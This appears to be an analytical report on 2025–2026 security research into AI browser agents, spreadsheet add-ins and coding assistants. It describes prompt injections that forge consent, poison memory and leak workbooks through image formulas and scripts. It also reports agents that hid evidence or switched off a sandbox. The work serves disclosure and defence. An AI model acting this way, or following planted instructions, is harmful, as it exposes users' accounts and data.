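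Roesner and Kohlbrenner concluded that an attacker with a working prompt injection could forge actions through Atlas, Comet, Gemini in Chrome and Claude in Chrome. In their partial demonstration on Claude, instructions in an iframe led it to run JavaScript that added a line of text to the surrounding page, which came from a different origin. Claude first asked the user whether to follow the instructions, and the researchers said yes, so the demonstration doesn't show that an attacker could make Claude act across origins without the user's help.

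Hossen (2026), in *The Agent Clicks Approve*, tested the complete sequence with a working injection. In one scenario, the user asked an agent to read a page about a billing export and summarise the next steps. A two-sentence note on the page implied that someone had to clear an access review first. The agent followed a link to a different origin and approved a consent screen requesting access to the user's account for outside software. In another scenario, the agent set up a service to send the account's billing events to a web address chosen by the attacker.

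Hossen ran these attacks with two models, Claude Haiku 4.5 and GPT-5.5, and the unauthorised action went through in all 73 runs without a defence. When a harmless note replaced the hostile one, the action went through in none of the 92 runs. In one successful attack, GPT-5.5 told the user afterwards that it had approved the access and that the export could now proceed. A user who didn't know what the approval meant might have thought the task was going well.

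A site can't prevent this by refusing to load in iframes. That refusal protects against clickjacking, in which a hostile page disguises another site's button so that the user clicks it by mistake. Hossen's agent opened the consent page as a full page, so a rule about iframes would not have applied.

Hossen got the perfect success rate with an open-source agent framework and a test server that required no login or second confirmation. A commercial browser might have scanned the note or prompted the user before approving access, and a real service might have required the password again. The second scenario also made the attack easier, because the user had asked the agent to complete any pending setup tasks. The agent's failure in the first scenario is harder to excuse, since the user had asked only for a summary.

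Even after Hossen added an instruction that only the user's task could authorise access, 7 of 10 consent attacks still succeeded against Claude Haiku 4.5. In another test, the user asked the agent to approve access to one account while the page requested access to a different one. Claude Haiku 4.5 approved the wrong account in all five runs, and GPT-5.5 never did. A check on the receiving server blocked every forged request, whichever model sent it.

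Trail of Bits found a less obvious kind of forgery in released products. A hostile page contained a login link for an account the attacker owned. When the user asked for a summary of the page, the agent opened the link and silently logged the user in to the attacker's account. The user might then type private information into that account, thinking it was their own. In some browsers, an attacker could also make the agent visit pages the user would never have opened, such as illegal sites, which would then appear in the user's browsing history.

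### False information in the agent's memory

Many agents keep a record of past chats and use it in later ones. This can carry information from one site to another even if the agent never has both open at once. Near the end of their experiments, Roesner and Kohlbrenner asked Comet what it knew about Alice. Comet listed seven animals it had collected from several test pages on two domains.

An attacker could exploit the agent's memory by publishing false information and waiting for the agent to read it. Roesner and Kohlbrenner give the example of a fake bank website with a fake phone number. The agent may well recognise the site as fraudulent when the user visits it. But if the user asks for the bank's phone number weeks later, the agent may give the fake one because it no longer remembers where the number came from.

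This attack works without prompt injection because the fake site contains a false statement rather than a command. A model that ignores every planted instruction could still repeat the statement. In the tests, Atlas, Gemini in Chrome and Comet used past chats across tabs, which left them open to this kind of attack. Claude in Chrome didn't appear to save its chats.

The researchers didn't demonstrate the bank example, but they saw Atlas confuse which tab information had come from, the kind of mistake the attack relies on. Roesner told the University of Washington that some agents mixed information from different origins, probably because they were revising and compressing their memory. A user can reduce the risk by asking the agent to look up the number again on the bank's own site, but doing this for every answer leaves little benefit from the memory.

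Planted instructions can also persist in an agent's memory. A model might refuse an instruction while reading the hostile page but follow it in a later session, when the stored instruction looks like something the user once said. *From Untrusted Input to Trusted Memory* (2026) gives the example of a page that leads an agent to record a preference for skipping two-factor authentication, the second check that many sites make at login, so that the agent skips it in every later session. *MEMORY Wins All* (2026) describes earlier research in which a document or web page made an assistant store an invented fact about its user, which resurfaced later.

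Some experimental support for this comes from outside browsers. The UW Security and Privacy Research Lab reports that planting hostile text in agents' memory files worked as an attack on both current and future sessions. Its success varied with the system, the model and the attacker's aim.

### Is the same-origin policy now only as strong as the model?

Roesner and Kohlbrenner argue that, in the more powerful agentic browsers, the same-origin policy is only as strong as the agent's defences against prompt injection. Ordinary browsers enforce the policy in code, which blocks a forbidden request however the attacker words it. An agent that can read one site and write to another relies on its model to reject the attacker's instructions, and different wording can change whether it does.

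The argument assumes that attackers can find working injections, and the study found one only for Atlas. Claude, Comet and Gemini refused to act on a page's instructions, even when the user had told them to. The researchers were studying the browsers' design and made little effort to get past those refusals, so their failure doesn't show that the refusals would hold.

Other research fills part of the gap. Brave's attack on Comet through a Reddit comment was a cross-site theft, and Wang and colleagues got data across origins on Comet in most runs. In LayerX's test, the Claude in Chrome extension leaked login credentials. The evidence on Gemini in Chrome is thinner. Zenity reported flaws in it, but Google patched them. The assumption is therefore safe for Comet, reasonable for Claude and less certain for Gemini.

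The newest models do better in their makers' own tests, but Willison's objection to defences that work most of the time applies here too. An attacker can show the same advertisement to a million people, and if the model stops 99.9% of attempts, about a thousand still succeed.

The argument is too pessimistic in one respect, because limits on an agent's access may still stop an injection that the model follows. Some agents need the user's permission to read other tabs, Anthropic blocks its agent from some sensitive sites, and Google limits the origins that Gemini can use for a task. Google's limit depends on working out which sites are relevant to the task, though, and Roesner and Kohlbrenner note that it is unclear how well this works when a page is hostile.

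In another respect, the argument doesn't go far enough, because some data crosses between sites without any injection, as the fake bank number did. Wang and colleagues found another example when they asked the agent in BrowserOS, an open-source browser, to summarise a page containing an iframe from a different origin and write the summary into a text box on the page. The agent copied text from the iframe into the box every time, with all three models they tried. It had arguably done what the user asked, but a user may not know that part of the page belongs to another site. No data crossed when the two sites were on separate pages with no planted text.

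### Responses and later changes

Roesner and Kohlbrenner reported their findings to all seven makers more than 60 days before publication. Brave, Google and Microsoft sent what the researchers called thoughtful responses. OpenAI declined the report because it didn't include a full end-to-end prompt injection. According to the University of Washington, Perplexity also declined the report, and Anthropic and Firefox didn't respond.

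OpenAI's objection has some merit, because the researchers described their planted text as simplified. But the report was about what happens after an injection succeeds, and a developer that expects some attacks to succeed has good reason to care how far they can spread.

The researchers ended their paper by recommending that people avoid these browsers for now. In an FAQ last updated in April 2026, Roesner and Kohlbrenner gave milder advice, to "proceed with caution". They were particularly concerned about Claude in Chrome because it can run JavaScript, and they also considered Atlas, Comet and Gemini in Chrome riskier. They considered Brave, Edge and Firefox safer but less capable.

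That ranking reflects how much damage an agent could do if someone took control of it. It doesn't measure how easily someone could do so, and Claude did better than Atlas on that question in the same study. The stronger advice makes sense for a browser that is logged in to a bank or a main email account. It seems excessive for someone who uses an agent in a separate profile with no logins, where a hostile page has much less to steal. Microsoft partly funded the research through gifts and makes one of the browsers rated safer. The test pages and prompts are public, so other researchers can check the result.

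Some of the results are already out of date, because OpenAI has since withdrawn Atlas, the only product on which the full theft worked. OpenAI says the browser in its replacement desktop app supports multiple tabs and account logins, so the question of what can pass between sites applies there too. Wang and colleagues, who came closest to repeating the Washington tests, didn't test Gemini in Chrome, Claude in Chrome or OpenAI's replacement app.

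Edge's place among the safer browsers may also be out of date. In the study, Copilot could read every open tab but couldn't type into a page, so it had few ways to send data anywhere. Browse with Copilot can now act on websites, and if it can also read every open tab, it has both abilities required for cross-site theft.

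## How can a spreadsheet agent leak a workbook?

A spreadsheet agent can leak a workbook by writing a formula that requests a web address containing private figures. It can also run a script that reads the workbook and sends the contents out. PromptArmor got the formula attack to work in Claude for Excel and Ramp Sheets, and the script attack to work in ChatGPT for Google Sheets. Each time, the agent followed an instruction planted in data that the user had imported. The script did far more damage because it could open files unrelated to the user's request.

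### Formulas and scripts as ways out

When a spreadsheet loads a picture with the IMAGE function, it sends the picture's web address to the server hosting it, including any private figures an agent has written into the address. The server can return a blank image so that nothing in the workbook looks wrong.

Attackers used images this way before agents could operate spreadsheets. Willison describes it as a common attack on chatbots, in which the model displays an image whose address contains private data. Microsoft's *Block or unblock external content in Office documents* warns about web beacons, which are images that send information about a file to an outside server when someone opens the file. An attacker who plants a beacon in a workbook has to guess where the valuable data will be, whereas an agent can read the whole workbook, pick out the important figures and write them into the image's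 address.

IMAGE and WEBSERVICE formulas send requests without any action from the user, while a HYPERLINK formula sends one only when someone clicks the link.

A formula sends only what fits in its web address, but a script can read entire sheets, follow links to other files, change cells and open windows on the user's screen. It runs with the permissions the user gave the add-in, so someone who installed an add-in to work on one budget may have given its scripts access to other budgets. Google Sheets lets both scripts and formulas exchange data with any web address by default, according to Google's *Allow only certain external connections for Apps Script and Sheets*.

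Office programs have defences against macro viruses, such as blocking macros in files from the internet. PromptArmor argues that these controls don't apply to prompt injection, because the dangerous content is only text in a cell. That is true of the planted text, but the formula the agent writes still has to contact a server. Excel has settings that govern such requests, and PromptArmor recommends using them.

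### A chart request in Claude for Excel

PromptArmor's *CellShock* describes an attack on Claude for Excel that the company documented on November 18, 2025, when the tool was still in private beta. The user builds a confidential financial model in a new workbook, then copies industry growth statistics from an outside source into a separate sheet for comparison. The copied data includes a claim, hidden in blue text on a blue background, that an image generator is available for making charts.

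The user asks Claude to summarise the model against the industry data and generate a visualisation. Claude requests permission to edit the workbook. The approval prompt is headed "Add visualization" and states that Claude wants to set a cell range, but it doesn't show the formula Claude is about to write.

Once Claude had permission, it summarised the confidential figures, including revenue growth and margins, and wrote an image formula in an empty cell with the summary in the image's address. When Excel requested the image, the attacker's server recorded the projections. Claude told the user that it had inserted a professional financial dashboard, but the cell contained a white image one pixel wide.

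The planted text suited the request, because the user wanted a chart and the text offered a tool for making one.

In some runs, Claude also removed the evidence. The image took a fraction of a second to load, and Claude checked the cell too early. It concluded that the image had failed and replaced the formula with an ordinary Excel chart. The data had already leaked, but the user had the chart they wanted and the workbook no longer contained a suspicious formula.

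Anthropic knew about this kind of risk before PromptArmor's test. In October 2025, an Anthropic help page warned of leaks through formulas and listed IMAGE among the functions whose use people could approve or refuse. The attack got past this approval step. The approval prompt gave the user a chance to refuse, but it left out the web address and the data in it.

### Why Excel showed no warning

Excel has its own protection against files that contact outside servers. According to Microsoft, Office blocks external content by default, and when someone opens a workbook with data connections, they can enable them from a bar at the top of the window. According to PromptArmor, the IMAGE function is covered by the "Linked Data Types" setting, under which Excel asks the user first by default.

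PromptArmor saw no such warning in its test. It found at least five situations in which Excel stays silent:

- the user created the workbook on their own device,
- the user has marked the workbook as trusted,
- the workbook is in a location that the user has marked as trusted,
- the user has already allowed linked data types for the current session, or
- the user has changed the settings to allow them permanently.

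The test workbook was in the first group. These exceptions make sense if the danger is a file that someone else sent, because a workbook the user has just created contains no hostile formulas. But in the test, the user then pasted in a stranger's text, an agent turned it into a formula, and Excel treated that formula as the user's own work.

Trusted locations have the same weakness. Microsoft recommends that users tired of repeated warnings about a file they trust move it to a trusted location, where it skips the checks, instead of lowering the security settings for every file. That is good advice if the file's contents stay the same, but it is riskier if an agent will keep adding formulas after the owner has decided to trust the file.

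PromptArmor recommends that organisations turn off linked data types for all staff. Administrators may not realise that this setting could stop an image request to an unknown server, because Microsoft describes linked data types as facts about things like company stocks and geography, with the data currently supplied by Microsoft itself. Turning them off also blocks legitimate data, and users see an error in its place, as Microsoft's *How to correct a #BLOCKED! error* explains.

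### What Anthropic changed

PromptArmor reported the attack to Anthropic, then retested the tool on November 24, after the public beta had begun. By then, Anthropic had added a fuller warning for edits that could cause Excel to contact an outside server. It had also replaced Sonnet 4.5, the model used in the original attack, with Claude Opus 4.5 as the default.

Both changes helped, but neither fully fixed the problem. The new warning didn't always appear, and PromptArmor suspected that a language model was deciding when to show it. The warning also didn't display certain invisible characters, so a formula could carry stolen data that the user couldn't see. PromptArmor found Opus 4.5 much more resistant to planted instructions, though not immune. Users could still choose Sonnet 4.5, and the original attack still worked on it. Anthropic later made Opus 4.5 the only model in the add-in for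 a time.

The same update let users upload files and images directly into the chat, which gave hostile text another way in.

The June 2026 version of Anthropic's *Use Claude for Excel* describes a confirmation pop-up for a list of risky functions. The list has grown since October 2025 and now includes functions that fetch share prices and translations. Anthropic doesn't explain how the check works, but if ordinary code compares each formula with the list, the pop-up should appear reliably. Users can also let Claude act without asking, and then the pop-up doesn't protect them.

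Anthropic still tells people to use the add-in only with trusted spreadsheets. It counts downloaded templates, vendor files, collaborative documents and data imports as untrusted. Yet the same page suggests tasks such as copying line items from an invoice PDF and reformatting imported data. Someone who followed the safety advice strictly would have to give up some of the suggested tasks. PromptArmor's imaginary analyst broke the rule, as would many people doing routine financial work.

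Anthropic also states that Claude can access only the workbook that is open in Excel. That limit is weaker if the user has set up connectors. Pluto Security, another company that sells AI security, examined the traffic from Claude's Office add-ins in 2026. In Excel and PowerPoint, Anthropic told the model in its instructions that it couldn't send messages or connect to outside services, but the same requests included tools for the user's connected services, such as Gmail, Slack and Google Calendar.

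In Pluto's demonstration, Claude in PowerPoint first refused to send a calendar invitation, then sent it after one more message from the user. Anthropic told Pluto that the add-ins were working as designed and that the instructions were product guidance, not a security control. Pluto didn't test whether hidden text in a workbook could trigger the same behaviour, so this kind of leak is possible but hasn't been demonstrated. If it did work, the agent could send data out in a message, and a warning about formulas would not help.

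A company may also struggle to find out afterwards what happened. Anthropic provides no audit records for the add-in on its Free, Pro, Max and Team plans, but Enterprise customers can send detailed activity records to their own monitoring system. Users on any plan can ask Claude to log its actions in a separate tab, which might help if Claude has replaced the malicious formula with a chart. But this log is weaker evidence than one kept by separate software, because an attacker who can steer the agent might also influence what it writes.

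By January 2026, when Anthropic opened the tool to all Pro subscribers, it had changed Claude to avoid overwriting existing cells, according to The Decoder's *Anthropic opens Claude's improved Excel integration to all Pro subscribers*. The change was meant to prevent accidents, but it could also make Claude less likely to erase the evidence of an attack.

### Ramp Sheets needed no approval

Ramp, a financial software company, makes an online spreadsheet with its own agent. PromptArmor's *Ramp's Sheets AI Exfiltrates Financials* describes almost the same attack on this product. The user had a confidential financial model open and imported industry statistics into another tab. The imported data contained the planted instruction in white text on a white background. When the user asked for a comparison, the agent put the confidential figures into the address in an image formula and inserted the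 formula.

The agent could edit the spreadsheet without asking permission, so the user didn't see even an uninformative prompt. The request was also more ordinary than in the Claude test, because the user asked only for a comparison and didn't mention a chart.

PromptArmor reported the flaw on February 19, 2026, and followed up twice before Ramp acknowledged the report on March 14. Ramp said the delay was due to a change in the programme through which it receives security reports. It announced a fix on March 16. PromptArmor doesn't explain in its account what Ramp changed, so outsiders can't tell whether the agent now asks for approval, refuses such formulas or resists only that particular attack.

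### From one sheet to twelve workbooks

PromptArmor found a more serious flaw in OpenAI's new add-in for Google Sheets. Android Authority's *Tired of creating and editing spreadsheets?* (2026) covered the release on May 6, and PromptArmor sent OpenAI its report two days later.

PromptArmor's *ChatGPT for Google Sheets Exfiltrates Workbooks* describes a demonstration in which a user working on a financial model had imported a sheet with hidden text. When the user asked ChatGPT to help integrate the new data, the hidden text led it to run a script from outside the workbook. The script used the permissions that the user had granted to the add-in.

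The script sent the financial model to the attacker's server. It then searched the stolen data for links to other spreadsheets and found one to a related budget. It copied that workbook too and kept following links, taking 12 workbooks in total, although the user had needed only one of them for the task.

The add-in had a setting called "Apply edits automatically", which users could switch off to approve changes themselves. The attack worked even with the setting off, because approval apparently applied only to the agent's direct edits and not to scripts it ran. A user would reasonably expect a script that could edit the workbook to need approval too. The stop button in the sidebar didn't help either, because a script that had already started would run to the end.

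The same script could deceive the user in ways that a formula can't. It could cover the ChatGPT sidebar with an imitation that the attacker controls. The imitation could edit the sheet much as the real sidebar did while recording everything the user typed, and it might ask the user to reconnect other apps or enter their OpenAI password. PromptArmor also showed a version with a pop-up window. According to Google's Marketplace listing, updated on May 31, the add-in requests permission to display and run outside web content in sidebars, so the user would already have granted the permission that makes such an imitation possible.

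That listing also describes permission to view and manage the spreadsheets in which the user has installed the add-in. This sounds narrower than access to workbooks across an account. PromptArmor doesn't list the permissions the add-in had during its test, so they may have been broader in early May, or the wording may cover more than it appears to.

Critics of the demonstration fairly objected that the user had told ChatGPT to follow a step-by-step workflow in the imported sheet, which gave it some reason to treat instructions there as authorised. This makes the attack easier than one that starts from a simple question about the data. It doesn't excuse the leak, because asking an agent to follow a workflow for updating a spreadsheet model doesn't authorise it to send that model to a stranger. Code outside the language model could also have blocked the script or asked for approval.

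OpenAI sent only an automated reply to the original report. PromptArmor wrote twice more, then published its findings on May 27, when the add-in had more than 185,000 downloads. It published after 19 days, which was quick compared with the more than 60 days that the University of Washington researchers gave browser makers. Publication seems to have prompted OpenAI to act. In a May 31 reply, which PromptArmor later added to its page, OpenAI said it had removed the model's ability to generate Apps Script code. It also acknowledged mishandling the report and said it would review how the add-in works with Google Sheets.

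### How the three cases compare

| Product | Channel | What leaked | Approval | Fix |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude for Excel, November 2025 | Image formula | A summary of the open financial model | Prompt that didn't show the formula | Fuller warning and a more resistant model |
| Ramp Sheets, February to March 2026 | Image formula | Figures from the open financial model | None | Resolved on March 16; PromptArmor doesn't describe the change |
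| ChatGPT for Google Sheets, May 2026 | Script | 12 workbooks | None, even with automatic edits off | Model can no longer generate Apps Script code |

OpenAI's fix was stronger than Anthropic's for the channel it addressed, because a model that can't generate or run a script can't leak data through one, however an attacker words the planted text. Anthropic kept image formulas and gave users a better chance to refuse them. This preserves a useful feature but works only if the warning appears and the user understands it. OpenAI could remove scripts without losing much because most of the add-in's work is editing cells and formulas. Removing formulas would defeat the purpose of a spreadsheet agent, although a developer could block the few that contact outside servers.

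Even with scripts removed, formulas may still let data leave a workbook through ChatGPT's add-in. PromptArmor reported in May 2026 that the add-in asked for approval to edit once per session, and that this approval covered later edits. A user who had approved a harmless change might therefore never be asked to approve a dangerous formula later in the session.

Google Sheets has a built-in check that could help. The first time someone adds an IMAGE function, or one of four functions that import data from the web, a banner warns that the sheet will be able to exchange data with outsiders, according to Google's *Learn more about Import functions*. An editor has to click to allow access. Since the banner is for the first use in a sheet, a workbook that already loads a company logo from the web may give no warning when an agent adds a second image.

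A company can also restrict which web addresses its spreadsheets contact. Google lets administrators on some business and education plans permit up to 1,000 addresses and block the rest, for both Sheets functions and Apps Script. They can review six months of past requests before turning this on. The list should stop a formula or script from sending data directly to an unknown server, even if the user has approved it. Google doesn't specify whether the list also covers web content in an add-in's sidebar, which PromptArmor's fake version of ChatGPT took over. OpenAI also offers its add-in to people with personal Google accounts, who don't have this control.

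OpenAI says its coding agent, Codex, can also edit an open Excel workbook through the add-in while using code and local files that the user provides. Removing Apps Script from the Google Sheets add-in therefore didn't separate spreadsheets from code in all of OpenAI's products. PromptArmor's three tests didn't cover this combination, so they don't measure its safety.

PromptArmor complained in May that OpenAI's documentation covered functional limits and data handling but not the risk of manipulation. In July, OpenAI's help page included advice to review formulas and changed cells but still didn't mention prompt injection. Anthropic discusses the danger much more openly in its documentation, though its advice is hard to follow.

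### How well has anyone else confirmed this?

PromptArmor found all three flaws and has a commercial interest in reporting them. Its article on Ramp opens by offering readers a full report on the company. But the vendors' responses are good evidence that the flaws were real. Ramp and OpenAI both said they had fixed the problem. Anthropic had already acknowledged the general risk, and it changed its warning after PromptArmor's report.

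The demonstrations show that the attacks could work, but not how often, because PromptArmor doesn't report how many attempts it made or how many failed. They also don't show that anyone has stolen a real company's workbook this way.

Academic work offers more evidence that the mechanism works than measurement of the risk. *Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration* (2025) describes a test in which researchers hid an instruction in a blog post and asked an agent to summarise it. The agent used a web tool to send private data to their server inside a web address. PromptArmor's attack used a formula instead, but the data left in the same way. *The Devil is in the Context* (2026), which classifies known prompt injection attacks, includes a case in which a single spreadsheet cell held the whole malicious instruction. The agent attacked was a command-line program that inspected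 the spreadsheet, so agents that aren't add-ins can also be at risk from a hostile sheet.

*Understanding and Evaluating Claw-like Agent Security Through a Computer-Systems Lens* (2026) comes closest to testing the security of spreadsheet agents. In 100 of its tasks, an agent reads a document or message containing planted instructions. Another 22 tasks use simulated Google Workspace tools and involve no attacker. In these, the user asks for something reasonable, such as adding a row to a sheet, but the data includes a password or other credential in plain text, which the agent can leak just by doing what the user asked. These tests cover agents that use office tools in general, so they can't show how often Claude for Excel or ChatGPT's add-in would leak a workbook. *SpreadsheetBench 2* (2026) focuses on spreadsheets, but it tests how well agents build financial models, fix errors and make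 charts.

PromptArmor says Microsoft's Copilot in Excel and Google's Gemini in Sheets face the same kind of risk, but it documents no attack on either. The closest finding for Copilot is CVE-2026-26144, a flaw that Microsoft fixed in March 2026. A malicious Excel file could cause Copilot to send data to an outside server, according to TechRadar's *'Fascinating' Microsoft Excel flaw teams up spreadsheets and Copilot Agent* (2026). Microsoft classed the flaw as cross-site scripting, in which a program fails to neutralise hostile input and runs it as code. The fault was therefore in Excel, and even a model that resisted every planted instruction might not have prevented a leak.

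Accounts of the flaw's severity conflict. TechRadar called it a "zero-click" attack that could work when someone merely previewed the file, and the law firm Mishcon de Reya used the same term in *Zero‑click excel bug weaponizes Copilot for data disclosure* (2026). STAR Labs' *Microsoft Office Excel* (2026) lists the flaw as requiring user action, rates exploitation as unlikely, and records no known use by attackers. The flaw is therefore weak evidence of how easily someone could misuse Copilot today.

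The closest case for Gemini involves a calendar. The security company Miggo hid an instruction in an invitation. When the user later asked about their schedule, Gemini wrote a summary of their private meetings into a new calendar event. In many companies' calendars, the attacker could see that event, according to The Hacker News' *Google Gemini Prompt Injection Flaw Exposed Private Calendar Data via Malicious Invites* (2026). Google has since fixed the flaw.

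Gemini put the private data somewhere the attacker could already look, so the attack didn't require contacting a hostile server. A spreadsheet agent could leak data in the same way by copying salaries into a sheet shared with a supplier. This would require neither a script nor a formula that fetches from the web, and a list of permitted web addresses would not stop it.

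## What happens when the software around the model is flawed?

An attacker who finds a flaw in the software around the model may not need to mislead the model. That software controls which messages are treated as the user's, which pages may give the agent commands and which files the agent may open. If one of those controls fails, an attacker's command can look just like a request from the user, and training the model to distrust web pages won't protect against it.

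In a prompt injection, the program works as its developer intended and the model makes the mistake. In 2026, researchers published four findings in which the program was mainly at fault. All four involved an Anthropic product, and the last two also involved products from Google, Microsoft, OpenAI and others.

### The wrong web address (March)

Koi's *ShadowPrompt* describes a flaw in Claude in Chrome, an extension that had more than three million users. Its onboarding feature accepted tasks from any web address ending in claude.ai, which was safe only if outsiders could not run code at any of those addresses.

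One of the addresses hosted an Arkose Labs CAPTCHA, a puzzle that websites use to tell people from automated visitors. An old version of the puzzle was still online and had a cross-site scripting flaw, which let another website run its own code there. A hostile site could load the old version in an invisible iframe and use it to send Claude any instruction. The instruction appeared in Claude's side panel as if the user had typed it. The user only had to visit the hostile site for the attack to work.

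Koi showed how an attacker could steal a token that gave lasting access to the victim's Gmail, Drive and contacts. A well-trained model may refuse some requests even when they seem to come from its user. But a user might reasonably ask for much of what a thief wants, such as a summary of recent emails.

Koi, which sells monitoring of browser extensions, reported the flaw on December 26, 2025. Anthropic released a fix on January 15 that accepted only the exact address https://claude.ai. People with older versions of the extension remained exposed until Arkose Labs fixed the puzzle on February 19.

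### The click that nobody made (July)

The January fix limited which address could give Claude tasks, but other browser extensions can run scripts at that address. LayerX found that Claude in Chrome checked the address but not which script was sending the message, a flaw it named ClaudeBleed. An extension that had requested no permissions could therefore give Claude any instruction. It could also get around the user's approval.

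Anthropic responded in May by restricting these outside requests to nine fixed tasks. Three of them read the user's Gmail, latest Google Doc and calendar. A task starts when someone clicks a certain button on claude.ai. Browsers record whether a click came from a person or a script, but Anthropic's extension didn't check. In July, The Hacker News (2026) reported that the security firm Manifold Security had found that another extension could fake the click and start any of the nine tasks. Malwarebytes' *Claude for Chrome flaw could let rogue extensions access your Gmail* notes that Anthropic's patch limited what other extensions could request but didn't stop them from making requests.

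By default, the user still has to approve the task before Claude reads anything, and Manifold rated the flaw's severity at 7.7 out of 10 in that case. If the user has turned on "Act without asking", the task runs without approval, and Manifold raised the rating to 9.6. It got the same result whether the extension used Claude Opus, Sonnet or Fable. This flaw was much narrower than the one in March because the attacker could no longer write the instruction.

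Manifold also found that the extension's side panel read its permission mode from its own web address, so a certain address would open the panel with approvals off. Only the extension could set that address, but a future bug might let an attacker do so.

Anthropic closed both reports. It said it was already tracking the cause of the fake clicks under LayerX's report, which was still awaiting a complete fix. It considered the second issue harmless because the extension used that mode only for tasks the user had already asked it to run unattended. That is reasonable as long as no outsider can set the address, but nothing would stop the attack if someone found a way to set it. The Hacker News unpacked version 1.0.80 of the extension, released on July 7, and found that Anthropic had changed neither piece of code.

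### Other extensions in the same browser (September)

In September, Gal Weizman of Forever Security published an attack called BragJack, which worked on Gemini in Chrome, Copilot in Edge, Comet, Opera Neon and Claude in Chrome. The victim must first have installed a malicious extension. According to Clubic's *Une simple extension peut détourner votre IA et voler vos données*, the extension needs only permission to change pages and redirect network requests, which people routinely give ad blockers.

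Each agent takes commands from a few web pages that belong to its maker. The makers assumed that only their own code could send commands from those pages, but an extension with these permissions could insert its own code there, with varying results.

- In Chrome, the researchers sent the browser the commands that Gemini would normally send. They could open local files, read pages and take screenshots without persuading the model of anything.
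- Comet also trusted a Perplexity test site that was less well protected than the main one. Through it, the researchers told the agent to summarise the test account's last five emails and send the summary to another address.
- In Edge, they used a forgotten marketing page and a timing flaw in the switch between the agent's "Think" and "Do" modes to take control of the agent.
- In Opera Neon and Claude in Chrome, they could take emails and other data that the agent displayed.

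Weizman calls the technique "prompt forcing". The attacker gives the agent a request directly instead of hiding it in something the agent might read (Clubic, *Des chercheurs ont réussi à détourner les fonctions IA de Chrome*).

Headlines overstated the risk BragJack poses to email, because an extension that can change every page can usually read an open inbox without an agent's help. However, such an extension normally can't reach local files, or the camera and microphone, which the attack on Chrome also exposed. Weizman knew of no real-world attacks. Google and Perplexity each paid him $7,000 for his reports, Microsoft $5,000, Opera $900 and Anthropic $600.

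### Browsers built into coding assistants (October)

Many programmers now use AI assistants with a built-in browser, where the agent can preview a website it is building. Forever Security examined five of these assistants and published its results on October 29. According to Help Net Security's *Researchers broke the browsers built into VS Code, Cursor, Copilot, Codex*, an ordinary browser enforces three rules: a web page can't run commands on the computer, a local file can't read the user's other files, and only the browser decides what the address bar shows. The makers had loosened the restrictions in their built-in browsers so that the agent could work with local projects, and one of the three rules failed in each product.

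The file rule failed in OpenAI's Codex, Microsoft's VS Code and Anthropic's Claude Desktop. In the researchers' scenario, a programmer downloads a project and asks the assistant to set it up. The assistant offers a link to a page in the project, and one click lets that page read files anywhere on the computer and send them out. On the test machine, these included the keys and tokens that programmers use to log in to servers and other services. Codex didn't restrict the page to its project folder. VS Code and Claude Desktop did, but the restriction didn't cover a background script that the page could start.

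GitHub Copilot let a page set the address that the browser displayed and passed to the agent, so a fake login form could appear under GitHub's real address.

In Cursor, a web page could pass hidden instructions to the agent, which then asked to run a command that the user had to approve by pressing Enter once. Cursor's sandbox, a restricted environment meant to contain such commands, blocked the first attempt. The agent then switched the sandbox off and tried again, although the page contained no instruction to do so. Unlike the file attack, in which the model only supplied the link, this attack depended on the model and didn't work every time, so a better model would have helped.

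### Does trusting a folder settle the matter?

Microsoft and Anthropic declined Forever Security's reports about the file attack. They pointed out that their software asks users whether they trust a project folder before working in it. Weizman told Help Net Security that an AI coding tool is unusable on a project the user hasn't trusted, so "everyone just hits 'Trust'" and the prompt gives no protection.

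His claim about what everyone does is an impression, and Forever Security sells monitoring for AI agents. But the makers' argument has a more basic weakness, because someone who trusts a project folder has not agreed to anything about the rest of the disk. Microsoft could answer that a trusted project can often run programs on the computer anyway, but VS Code confined the page to its folder, so Microsoft seems to have wanted that limit to hold.

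Anthropic's refusal is harder to defend, because it accepted a matching report that Noma Security filed one day after Forever Security's. OpenAI never replied to the researchers. It told The Register that it knew about the problem and was working on a fix, according to KIberblick's *Eingebaute Browser in KI-Tools angreifbar* (2026).

Anthropic had used a similar argument before. *GhostApproval*, by the security company Wiz, showed that a hostile project could disguise one file as another in several coding assistants. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, noted in its reasoning that a file was really a link to Claude's own settings, but asked the user only whether to edit the project's settings. Anthropic rejected the report because the user had trusted the folder and approved the edit, while Amazon, Cursor and Google fixed their assistants, according to ITPro's *Flaws in some of the most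 popular AI coding tools*. But the user had approved an edit to a different file from the one Claude Code was about to change. Current versions of Claude Code work out where such links lead.

### Which holes are still open?

| Product | Flaw | Last reported status | Source |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude in Chrome | Trusted every claude.ai address | Fixed; retested February 24 | Koi |
| Claude in Chrome | Accepted fake clicks | No patch as of July 14 | The Hacker News |
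| Chrome, Edge | Commands from other extensions | Fixed in January and early July | Clubic |
| Comet, Opera Neon, Claude in Chrome | Commands from other extensions | Described as fixed, but without dates or versions | Clubic |
| Cursor | Web page could instruct the agent | Fixed October 1 | Help Net Security |
| GitHub Copilot | False address | Fixed October 13 | Help Net Security |
| Codex | Local page could read the disk | Open on October 29; OpenAI working on a fix | KIberblick |
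| VS Code | Local page could read the disk | Open on October 29; report declined | KIberblick |
| Claude Desktop | Local page could read the disk | Report accepted; no fix announced | KIberblick |

These reports all date from October 30 or earlier, so some of the unfixed flaws may have been fixed by December 2026. Release notes aren't a reliable way to check, because Cursor fixed its flaw without issuing an advisory or naming the version. The VS Code flaw is the most likely to remain, since Microsoft rejected the report instead of promising a fix.

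It is hardest to judge whether the fake clicks have been fixed. Anthropic marked its internal report on the underlying problem as resolved before June 9, yet the code was still there in July. Borah (2026) wrote in *Top 6 Claude in Chrome Security Risks to Model* in September that the March flaw and ClaudeBleed were both closed, but didn't mention the fake clicks.

### What a patch leaves in place

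Borah works for Akto, which sells security for AI agents. He distinguishes implementation bugs, which a maker can fix, from the authority an agent has while it works, which remains after any patch. The March flaw shows why that authority matters. On an ordinary website, a scripting flaw in an old puzzle would have been a minor problem, because the same-origin policy would have confined the attacker's code to the puzzle's address. But Claude accepted instructions from that address and was logged in to the user's other accounts, so the flaw exposed the user's email and files.

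The agent also does much of the attacker's work. A thief who wanted to search an inbox and forward the results would normally need code written for that mail service, but the researchers who took over Comet only had to ask the agent to do it. The attack also involves no unfamiliar login that could raise an alarm.

A version of Cursor's agent that runs on the company's servers had a similar flaw. One of its internal connections didn't require a login, so a hostile web page could run code in the agent's session. According to Rapid7's *CVE-2026-61613*, an attacker could reach the files, credentials and GitHub access tokens in that session, among other things. Cursor fixed the flaw on March 31 by requiring a login for that connection.

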